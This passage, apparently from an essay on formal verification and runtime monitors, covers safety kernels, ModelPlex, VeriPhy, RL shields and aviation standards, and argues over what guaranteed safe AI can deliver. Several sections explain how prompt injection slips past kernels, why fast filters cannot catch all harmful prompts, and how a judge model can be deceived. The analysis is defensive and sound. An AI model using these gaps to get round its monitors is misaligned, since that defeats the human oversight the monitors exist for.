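Their running example is a water tank that must not overflow. The controller sets the flow f at least once every ε seconds, and the tank can hold m litres and now contains x. The monitor requires

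−1 ≤ f ≤ (m − x)/ε

If there is room for 0.6 litres, a controller that runs every two seconds may let in at most 0.3 litres per second. The monitor that checks this limit is a formula with 12 arithmetic, comparison and logical operators. The safety proof behind the monitor for an adaptive cruise control took 969 steps, but that monitor has only 78 operators, so an engineer could still read it in full. KeYmaera X produced the monitor in 3.3 seconds.

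ModelPlex also produces a second monitor, which checks whether the physical world behaves as the model predicts. Mitsch and Platzer simulated the tank with both monitors. Four seconds in, the controller requested too much water, and the first monitor caught the command before it took effect. At 12 seconds, an extra inflow of 0.05 litres per second began, which was not in the model. The controller's command was acceptable, so only the second monitor could detect the problem. It did so at the next check, two seconds later. The backup then kept the tank from overflowing because the disturbance was small. No monitor could guarantee safety without a limit on how far the world can depart from the model between checks.

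### From the formula to machine code

A correct formula can still fail as a program, for example if the computer rounds a number the wrong way. *VeriPhy* (Bohrer, Tan and colleagues, 2018) extends the proof to the machine code. The tool replaces each real number with a pair of whole numbers that the true value must lie between. If the interval is too wide to settle whether a command is safe, the program treats the command as unsafe. CakeML, a compiler with its own correctness proof, then produces the machine code.

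The trusted computing base is still large. It includes about 12,000 lines of code at the core of two theorem provers, a handwritten parser and the software that solves arithmetic problems. The system must also prevent the untrusted controller from altering the monitor's memory, and seL4 provides this kind of isolation.

Bohrer and colleagues tested VeriPhy on a small wheeled robot with a laser distance sensor. The robot started 75 centimetres from an obstacle, with a deliberately faulty controller that sped it up to the maximum of 25 centimetres per second as it got close. The robot could travel 5.5 centimetres between checks, so the monitor had to stop it once the gap was smaller than that. The backup controller took over at about 4.6 centimetres, and the robot stopped about 2.6 centimetres from the obstacle.

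The laser detected only about 94% of obstacles, and its readings could be off by up to 3 centimetres, which is more than the remaining gap. The researchers had allowed a margin for sensor and motor errors, but VeriPhy's theorem assumes exact measurements, so the proof alone would not have ruled out a collision on this hardware.

Bohrer, Tan and colleagues (2019), in *A Formal Safety Net for Waypoint Following in Ground Robots*, moved on to a simulated car that steers and accelerates. It drove three courses under several controllers and, for comparison, amateur human drivers, with no safety violations. The physics monitor raised more alarms than the controller monitor because the simulator's car moved in more complicated ways than the model's. After a physics alarm, the car braked, without the full guarantee, and then carried on. Because a car that never moves would also satisfy the safety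 theorem, the researchers proved separately that the car can always still reach its next waypoint.

### Shields for systems that are still learning

A reinforcement learning program learns by trying actions and receiving rewards, and some of those actions may be dangerous. A *shield* is a monitor that can operate even during this training. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (2017) describes a shield placed before the learner, which gives it a list of safe actions to choose from, and one placed after the learner, which replaces only unsafe actions. Platzer (2019), in *Overview of Logical Foundations of Cyber-Physical Systems*, describes a similar use of ModelPlex, whose monitors can form a verified sandbox around a learning program.

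If chance plays a part, the shield needs probabilities. Let p(s) be the lowest achievable probability of ever ending in disaster from state s, with p = 1 for the disaster itself. If P(s′ | s, a) is the probability that action a leads from s to s′, then

p(s) = minₐ Σ P(s′ | s, a) p(s′)

The sum for a single action is the risk of taking it and then behaving as safely as possible. The shield can block any action whose risk exceeds a chosen threshold.

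*Easy-to-Use Shielding for Reinforcement Learning* (2026) compares shielded and unshielded training in two small grid worlds, with five runs for each setting. In one world, the agent crosses a slippery floor beside lava. In the other, an adversary tries to catch the agent, and the shield assumes the adversary will make its best moves. With that shield, the agent could focus on learning its task instead of learning to avoid capture by trial and error.

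The tool generated its model of each world automatically from the game's own software. No such software exists for a road, so someone has to write the model and might leave out something important. The threshold also limits the risk of each choice separately, so an agent that takes a permitted 10% risk ten times has about a 65% chance of disaster.

### Rules and results from aviation

The aviation standard for this kind of system is ASTM F3269, *Standard Practice for Methods to Safely Bound Behavior of Aircraft Systems* (2021). It calls the untrusted part the complex function and the backup the recovery function. Designers must determine the conditions under which both the monitor and the recovery function are effective, and must not use the system outside those conditions. For instance, if the braking car's figure of 5 m/s² held only on dry roads, the car would have to stay off wet ones.

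Nagarajan and colleagues explain that the monitor and backup need the same level of assurance that the complex function would need on its own. In return, the designer can later upgrade the complex function with fewer changes to the aircraft's certification, much as the bill-paying company can replace its language model. The standard does not require a machine-checked proof, so a compliant monitor may have had only conventional reviews and tests.

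One of the standard's examples is a system that the US Air Force uses on its F-16s to prevent crashes into the ground. Here the untrusted component is the pilot, who may be disoriented or unconscious. When impact is imminent, an autopilot takes control, flies the aircraft clear of the terrain and returns control to the pilot.

More recent tests have used the X-62 VISTA, an F-16 that Lockheed Martin modified for experiments with autonomy. *Safety Guardrails in the Sky* (2026) reports flights from September 2024 with a monitor called Guardrails, which blends the pilot's commands with those of a backup controller instead of switching abruptly to the backup. It passed all 14 test points, including some in which pilots tried to push the aircraft past its limits. This is good evidence about the monitor, although a learned controller might fail in ways a test pilot would not think of.

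Jäger, Friedrich and colleagues (2026), in *Context-dependent Runtime Construction of Safe Regions of Attraction from Design-Time Identification*, point out that blending filters have to solve an optimisation problem while the vehicle is moving and can make its controls chatter. Simplex's weakness is that it must take over whenever the vehicle leaves the region in which the backup is certain to recover, and a cautious estimate makes that region small. Their system for mobile robots chooses among several backups to enlarge that region. It stayed safe when they injected faults, and also when the main controller had learned by imitation.

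Learned controllers now fly real fighters as well. DARPA (2026), the Pentagon's research agency, announced in July that an AI agent was controlling a converted F-16 from the regular fleet under human supervision. In August, D'Urso (2026) reported in *X-62 VISTA Conducts AI-Controlled Intercepts with IRST Pod* that AI agents had made 27 intercepts in eight flights, locating their targets with an infrared sensor. According to Bennet (2026), in *U.S. Air Force Test Pilot School Completes Two Accelerated X-62 VISTA Test*, the X-62 follows AI commands within limits that its users set. It is therefore a working example of the two-layer design, although successful flights do not prove that the limits always hold.

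These monitors also leave a good deal unchecked. According to *Mission-Level Runtime Assurance Framework for Autonomous Driving* (2026), those for self-driving cars mainly cover immediate dangers such as collisions or leaving the road. A detour could pass every check and still leave the car unable to complete its trip within its remaining budget.

### When a learned system measures the distance

The braking formula needs a value for d, which in many cars a neural network estimates from camera images. That network is then part of the trusted computing base, even if the network that drives the car is not.

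Suppose the vision network overestimates distances by 10%. The real gap is 40 metres and the network estimates 44, which is more than the 42.8 the monitor requires, so the monitor lets the car accelerate. A tenth of a second later the estimate has dropped to 41.8 metres and the monitor makes the car brake. By then the obstacle is 38 metres away and the car needs 40.8 metres to stop, so it hits the obstacle at about 5 m/s.

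An error in the physical model can be worse. If a wet road limits braking to 3 m/s², a car that starts braking at the last moment the formula allows will still be moving at almost 13 m/s when it reaches the obstacle. The proof covers neither case because it assumes accurate measurements and braking at 5 m/s².

The payment kernel can look up an account number in the bookkeeper's list, but no list contains the distance to a pedestrian.

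**Error bounds.** The proof can account for measurement error. Mitsch and Platzer do this for the water tank by assuming that the sensor is never wrong by more than a known amount u, and *Verified Runtime Validation for Partially Observable Hybrid Systems* (2018) extends ModelPlex to systems whose sensors measure the true state only approximately. For the car, the monitor would subtract u from the measured gap. With u = 4 metres, it would require a reading of 46.8 metres before letting the car accelerate, so it would have refused to allow this at a reading of 44 metres. The drawback is that a car with accurate measurements brakes four metres earlier than necessary.

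This works well for a sensor whose errors have a physical limit. The bound for a vision network comes from test images, and its errors may be larger on a scene unlike any of them. The network may also miss an obstacle, leaving no reading to subtract four metres from. The laser on the wheeled robot had the same weakness, since its 3-centimetre bound did not cover obstacles it failed to detect.

ASTM requires an *input manager* that examines untrusted data before the monitor uses it. The input manager rejects impossible values, such as a compass heading above 360 degrees, and compares readings with known patterns of behaviour. For example, when a vehicle approaches a stationary obstacle at a steady 20 m/s, the gap should shrink by 2 metres every tenth of a second. If a network overestimated the gap by 10%, the reported gap would shrink by 2.2 metres instead, and the input manager might detect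 this after several readings. But if the network always added four metres, the reported gap would still shrink by 2 metres each time and pass the check.

**Independent sensors.** The car could also carry a radar, and the monitor could use the shorter of the two distances. The proof then needs only one sensor to be right. How much this helps depends on how often both fail at once. Suppose each sensor misses one obstacle in 1,000. If the failures were independent, both would miss the same obstacle one time in a million. But suppose all the misses happen in heavy rain, which accounts for 1% of encounters, so that each sensor misses 10% of obstacles in the rain. Even if the sensors fail independently of each other in the rain, both miss the same obstacle one time in 10,000 overall, which is a hundred times as often.

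*Synergistic Simplex* (2026) warns that learned components are prone to such shared faults, so a second copy of the same network, or another network trained on the same images, may add little protection. Different algorithms or types of sensor share fewer weaknesses. The paper applies Simplex to perception itself, using a learned system and a safety-oriented one together to detect obstacles.

Using the shorter distance also means that a false alarm from either sensor makes the car brake, and sudden braking on a motorway is itself dangerous. But the vision network, like the payment kernel's fraud classifier, can only make the system more cautious, because the distance the system uses is never longer than the radar's reading. Even if the network fails completely, the guarantee holds as long as the radar detects the obstacle with an error within the bound and the brakes work as the model assumes.

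## What no kernel can decide

A kernel can block unsafe actions, but it cannot guarantee that useful work gets done. A car that never moves cannot hit an obstacle, and a payment kernel that refuses every payment satisfies all three of the company's rules but leaves its bills unpaid. Even a perfect kernel cannot guarantee honest invoices or sound advice. Better rules would close some of these gaps, but others would remain under any rules, because a kernel can only refuse actions and can only base its decisions on facts that a program can check.

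### Wrong acts and missing acts

When Rushby concluded in 1989 that kernels could provide safety, he meant protection from wrong acts. Ammann (1994), in *A Safety Kernel For Traffic Light Control*, applied Rushby's model to traffic lights and set out what it requires. The kernel must control everything that the safety rule mentions, and nothing outside the kernel may be able to break the rule. Let op be the set of all operations, inside the kernel or outside it, and let op* be the set of all sequences of them. To show that a kernel maintains a rule P, an engineer generally has to show that

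P(α) holds for every α ∈ op*

One of Ammann's rules is that when two directions of traffic conflict, at least one has a red light. A kernel in the traffic light's controller can reject any command that would break this rule. But a short circuit could turn on two green lamps without any command, so real traffic lights also have a separate hardware unit that detects conflicting signals whatever their cause.

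The company's daily limit has the same weakness. If the bookkeeper sometimes pays bills by hand through a separate bank login, those payments bypass the kernel. The kernel can guarantee only that the payments that go through it total no more than €5,000 a day.

A traffic light stuck on red in every direction would satisfy Ammann's rule. As Ammann notes, a kernel makes it easier to assess whether the lights are safe, but it does not help assess whether they let traffic through.

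### What a monitor can enforce

Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), made this limit precise. His result covers any monitor that watches a program's steps and halts the program before a step that would break a rule. Reference monitors and firewalls both work this way. The monitor cannot see the future or what the program might have done in other circumstances, so it can enforce a rule only if the rule meets these conditions:

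1. Each run of the program obeys or breaks the rule by itself, whatever other runs are possible.
2. Once a run has broken the rule, nothing that happens later can repair it.
3. Every run that breaks the rule does so after a finite number of steps.

Computer scientists call such rules *safety properties*. They require that a particular bad thing never happens. One example is "The assistant never pays an account that is not on the list." A single payment to an unlisted account breaks this rule, and no later payment can undo the violation.

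"The assistant eventually pays every invoice that the bookkeeper has approved" is not a safety property. Suppose an approved invoice has been waiting for a year. The assistant might still pay it tomorrow, so the kernel can never establish that the assistant has broken the rule. The kernel could refuse all the assistant's other requests until it pays, but the assistant could stop without paying. Schneider gives a similar example, in which a monitor can prevent a seller who has taken a customer's money from doing anything except deliver, but cannot make the seller deliver.

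Adding a deadline does not always make a rule enforceable. "The assistant pays every approved invoice within 30 days" meets all three conditions, because an unpaid invoice breaks it on day 31. The monitor still cannot enforce it, because stopping the program does not stop time from passing. Schneider points out that a limit on the program's steps would be enforceable. If the rule required payment within 100 actions of the approval, the kernel could uphold it by halting the assistant before the hundredth action, but the supplier would still be unpaid.

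The company could instead have a conventional program pay each approved invoice on its due date. Schneider's result does not rule this out, because the program starts payments rather than only stopping them. But payment would still depend on the bank's systems and on there being enough money in the account, and the company would have more code to check.

Secrecy fails the first condition because whether a program's output reveals a secret depends on what the output would have been if the secret had been different, and nobody can tell that from one run. Monitors that protect secrets therefore enforce stricter rules, as Tether does when it labels even a shopping list Sensitive. These stricter rules also block some harmless actions.

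### A false invoice that satisfies every rule

Suppose an approved cleaning firm invoices €1,800 for a month in which nobody cleaned. The firm's account is on the list, the amount is too small to need approval, and the day's total is within the limit. The kernel correctly applies its rules and allows the payment.

Checking the invoice against the order record does not help, because the company did order a month of cleaning. The company could add a rule requiring somebody to confirm delivery. This works well for 20 chairs, which a colleague can count. For cleaning or legal advice, somebody has to judge whether the firm did the work properly, and the kernel can check only that this person confirmed it.

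The same gap exists at the operating-system level. Zou and colleagues point out that an instruction hidden in a tool's reply is well-formed data, so it breaks no rule about system calls. If an agent writes a file with contents from a memory an attacker planted, the operating system registers an ordinary file write. For the same reason, some AgentDojo attacks succeeded on seL4 using only functions the agent needed for its task.

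Some harm involves no action that a kernel should refuse. Suppose the company asks its assistant to compare three bids for a cleaning contract. The assistant's only action is to show the bookkeeper a few paragraphs. These might favour one bidder because of hidden text in that bidder's proposal, or leave out a serious complaint about another. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a business plan that cuts costs by subtly recommending the exclusion of clients with certain characteristics. A kernel could control who receives such a text, but it has no exact rule for separating a fair recommendation from a biased one.

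Misleading text can also defeat the approval rule, even if the kernel enforces it correctly. If the assistant tells the bookkeeper that a supplier will go to court unless it receives €4,000 today, the bookkeeper may approve the payment. The approval is genuine, so the kernel allows the payment. A conventional program could show the payee, the amount and the order on the approval screen, so the bookkeeper does not have to rely on the assistant for those facts. The bookkeeper would still have to decide whether the court threat was real.

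### Why filters do not close the gap

A company might put a filter in front of a language model to catch harmful prompts. Ball and colleagues proved that filters much faster than the model cannot always do this. For any source of sufficiently varied harmless prompts, there is a model and a source of harmful prompts for it that no such filter can distinguish from the harmless ones. Producing the harmful prompts takes about as long as producing the harmless ones.

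The theorem depends on three assumptions:

- Time-lock puzzles exist. These are puzzles that someone can create quickly but that nobody can solve without a set amount of computation, even with many computers working in parallel.
- The filter has much less computing time than the model.
- The filter cannot use the model's weights or internal workings. Its designers may have tried any prompts they liked on the model beforehand.

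The assumption about computing time is realistic, because companies want filters that need little of it. The theorem would not apply to a filter as powerful as the model, but the company would then need some reason to trust the filter. Ball and colleagues also consider models that cooperate with an attacker, for example by sharing a secret key. No efficient filter can then recognise the harmful prompts, even with more computing time than the model. This result resembles the one about undetectable backdoors, and Goldwasser co-wrote both papers.

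The theorem proves that such a model exists, but doesn't show that today's models are like it. Ball and colleagues built their model for the proof and acknowledge that its behaviour is contrived. A filter might still catch nearly all the harmful prompts that people send to a real assistant. The theorem rules out a general method for building a fast filter that works for every model, without looking inside the model.

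Filtering the model's answers has a similar limit. Ball and colleagues proved that harmful answers can be indistinguishable from safe ones, even to a filter with more computing time than the model, but only where the harm itself is difficult to recognise. They note that where harm is easy to recognise, the filter is easy to build. The payment kernel can easily check whether an account is on the bookkeeper's list, so the theorem does not apply to it.

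Ball and colleagues conclude that an AI system's intelligence cannot be separated from its judgement. This is too strong for payments, because the bookkeeper makes the necessary judgement in advance by deciding which accounts go on the list. It fits the comparison of bids better, because judging the answer there takes about as much understanding as writing it.

### Who writes the policy

Even where a fixed rule would work, people have to choose the right one. Rushby (1993), in *Critical System Properties*, reports a study of faults found while testing the software of the Voyager and Galileo spacecraft. Of the 197 faults that could have seriously harmed the missions, three were coding errors. The other 194 came from the specifications of what the parts should do and how they should fit together. A proof that the code matched its specification would therefore have addressed at most three of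 these faults. Careful programmers had probably removed many coding errors before these tests, so the proportion would be different in an ordinary project.

The company's three rules have a mistake of this kind, because none of them prevents the assistant from paying the same invoice twice. Two payments of €1,500 to an approved supplier stay within every limit, and a proof of the kernel would still succeed. Schneider recommends deriving consequences from a formal rule, or running it on particular scenarios, and comparing the results with what people wanted. Testing a duplicate invoice would reveal the mistake, but only someone who had thought of duplicates would run that test.

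A specification can also permit too much by leaving things out. Rushby warns that proofs often show that a program does everything required of it without showing that it does nothing else. Suppose the company proves that the kernel sends the bank every payment the rules allow. The theorem would still be true if the kernel sent a few extra payments, so the specification must also state that it sends no others.

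Other choices are compromises, because people want different things. The engineer who sets up one of Ammann's traffic lights chooses how long each yellow light lasts, from 3 to 25.5 seconds, and how long conflicting directions must all stay red before one turns green. Longer delays give cars more time to clear the junction, but drivers will not put up with very long ones. The kernel enforces whatever the engineer chose. The company's daily limit is a similar compromise. A low limit protects the owner from fraud, but it makes some suppliers, who have no say in the limit, wait until the next day for their money.

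A small company can agree on rules for its AI systems in a short meeting. The most ambitious proposals for proof-based safety would require agreement on rules for AI systems that affect millions of people, which is much harder to reach.

### The case for guaranteed safe AI

Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably safe systems*, argue that proof is the only path to safe control of AI systems more intelligent than people. However intelligent a system becomes, it cannot do what is provably impossible. A proof may be very hard to find, but a simple program can check it with little computation. People could therefore let an untrusted AI system write both a program and its proof, and run the program only if the proof passes the check. Tegmark and Omohundro want secure hardware to enforce this, so that a DNA synthesizer, for instance, would not run without a proof of safety.

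They would have humans write the specifications, with help from AI, and they call producing the code and the proof "the two really hard steps". That part of their forecast has held up well, as the AI-written proofs of cryptographic libraries show.

Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, describe a broader family of methods with three components:

- A *world model* describes mathematically how the AI system affects its surroundings.
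- A *safety specification* states which effects are acceptable.
- A *verifier* produces a proof, or a bound on the probability of harm, that anyone can check.

The monitor for the braking car has all three. Its world model is the formula for stopping distance, its specification is that the car never hits the obstacle, and its verifier is a theorem prover.

Their case rests largely on the weakness of testing. OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months before releasing it, and users got around its safeguards within a day. More generally, Rushby's survey explains that to show by testing alone that a system typically runs for n hours before it fails, engineers need about n hours of testing without a failure. For a system that may fail only once in a billion hours, that is about 114,000 years. But Rushby also says that a formal proof does not justify a failure rate of zero, or any other number, because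 the proof is about a model of the system.

### Objections and replies

Dickson (2024) makes the same point about the physical world in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*. Engineers used formal verification to show that bugs would not make the Perseverance lander's software fail on Mars, but they proved nothing about the landing itself. By one analysis, software accounts for about 20% of the risk of failure in Mars missions, so perfect software would still leave about 80% of the risk.

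Martinez Suñe replies to Dickson that guaranteed safe AI does not require a failure rate of zero, because a specification can limit the probability of harm instead. This is a fair reading of Dalrymple and colleagues, though Tegmark and Omohundro write about making harm provably impossible. But a limit on probability also depends on the world model, just as the braking formula depends on a dry road.

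Dickson also argues that the most serious threats are too complex to model. He writes that a program would have to simulate a new virus and a human body over several years to predict whether the virus would harm people. In 2022, a leading simulation covered 20 minutes in the life of one unusually simple cell. The program would also lack the starting data. A Google project that mapped a millionth of a human brain produced 1.4 petabytes.

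A reader's comment on Dickson's essay calls this a straw man, because Dalrymple and colleagues give the example of a DNA synthesiser that provably cannot make *certain* pathogens, which does not require a simulated human body. The comment is right, and such a machine would be useful. But it would also be a kernel with a list, much like the bookkeeper's, and it would let through any dangerous sequence that nobody had thought to include.

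Dalrymple and colleagues also propose making the world model deliberately cautious. For example, an engineer who does not know how well a car will brake in the rain can assume the worst plausible figure. But a model cautious enough to be correct may rule out nearly everything. One commenter on *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, a post that defends the approach, calls it "risible" to claim that useful models of this kind are feasible. Another finds most of the programme premature but would keep the part about making software secure.

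Human psychology is probably the hardest case. A critic of the same post asks how anyone could specify that an AI system will not exploit human psychology, or write a cautious model of how people respond. Dickson makes a similar point about misinformation, noting that a genuine photograph can mislead people when someone presents it out of context. Dalrymple and colleagues concede that harm is difficult to define formally. They suggest using several specifications or learning them from data, but learning them would put a learned component back into the trusted computing base.

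They also say that the acceptable level of risk should ideally come from collective deliberation, but that doesn't settle how to turn the decision into a formula.

Hatfield-Dodds (2024) says in *Formal Verification is Overrated* that he likes formal verification but that many papers on it "substantially over-claim". That seems right about the debate so far. The proposals are convincing for systems with a few well-understood actions, such as logging in to a computer or paying a bill. For harm that depends on how people understand a text, making proofs easier to produce does not help, because nobody in this debate has produced a specification to prove a system against.

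### Letting a learned judge handle meaning

A natural response is to divide the work, much as Zou and colleagues do. The kernel would apply the fixed rules to each payment, and a second language model would judge the invoices and emails and refuse anything that looked wrong.

Ball and colleagues doubt that a learned judge can be relied on for this. To recognise every danger, it would have to be about as intelligent as the system it oversees, and then it is unclear why anyone would use the untrusted system at all. One answer is that the judge, like the fraud classifier, would only be able to refuse payments, so it could be useful without being more reliable than the assistant.

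Suppose the judge catches 95% of false invoices in tests. If the judge's mistakes are independent, a dishonest supplier who sends 20 different false invoices has about a 64% chance of getting at least one past it. A supplier who learns from each refusal will probably do better. And if the judge and the assistant are copies of the same model, a text that deceives one may well deceive the other.

Even if the assistant and the judge both fail completely, the kernel pays nothing to strangers and no more than €5,000 a day in total. But a dishonest supplier on the list could receive all €5,000 without anyone's approval, in two payments of €2,000 and one of €1,000. Over 250 working days, the total would be €1.25 million. A company that could not survive such a loss would need a lower limit for each supplier, or a person who compares the payments with the work every month.

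The judge also gives an attacker a new way to cause harm. Someone who makes a genuine electricity bill look suspicious can get the judge to refuse it, and the kernel cannot make the payment happen. The company should therefore send refused invoices to a person instead of discarding them.

For the comparison of bids, the kernel can guarantee only that the text goes to the bookkeeper and nobody else. If the judge misses a bias in the recommendation, no fixed rule will catch it, and the bookkeeper would have to read the three bids to find it. The judge is therefore part of the trusted computing base for that task.
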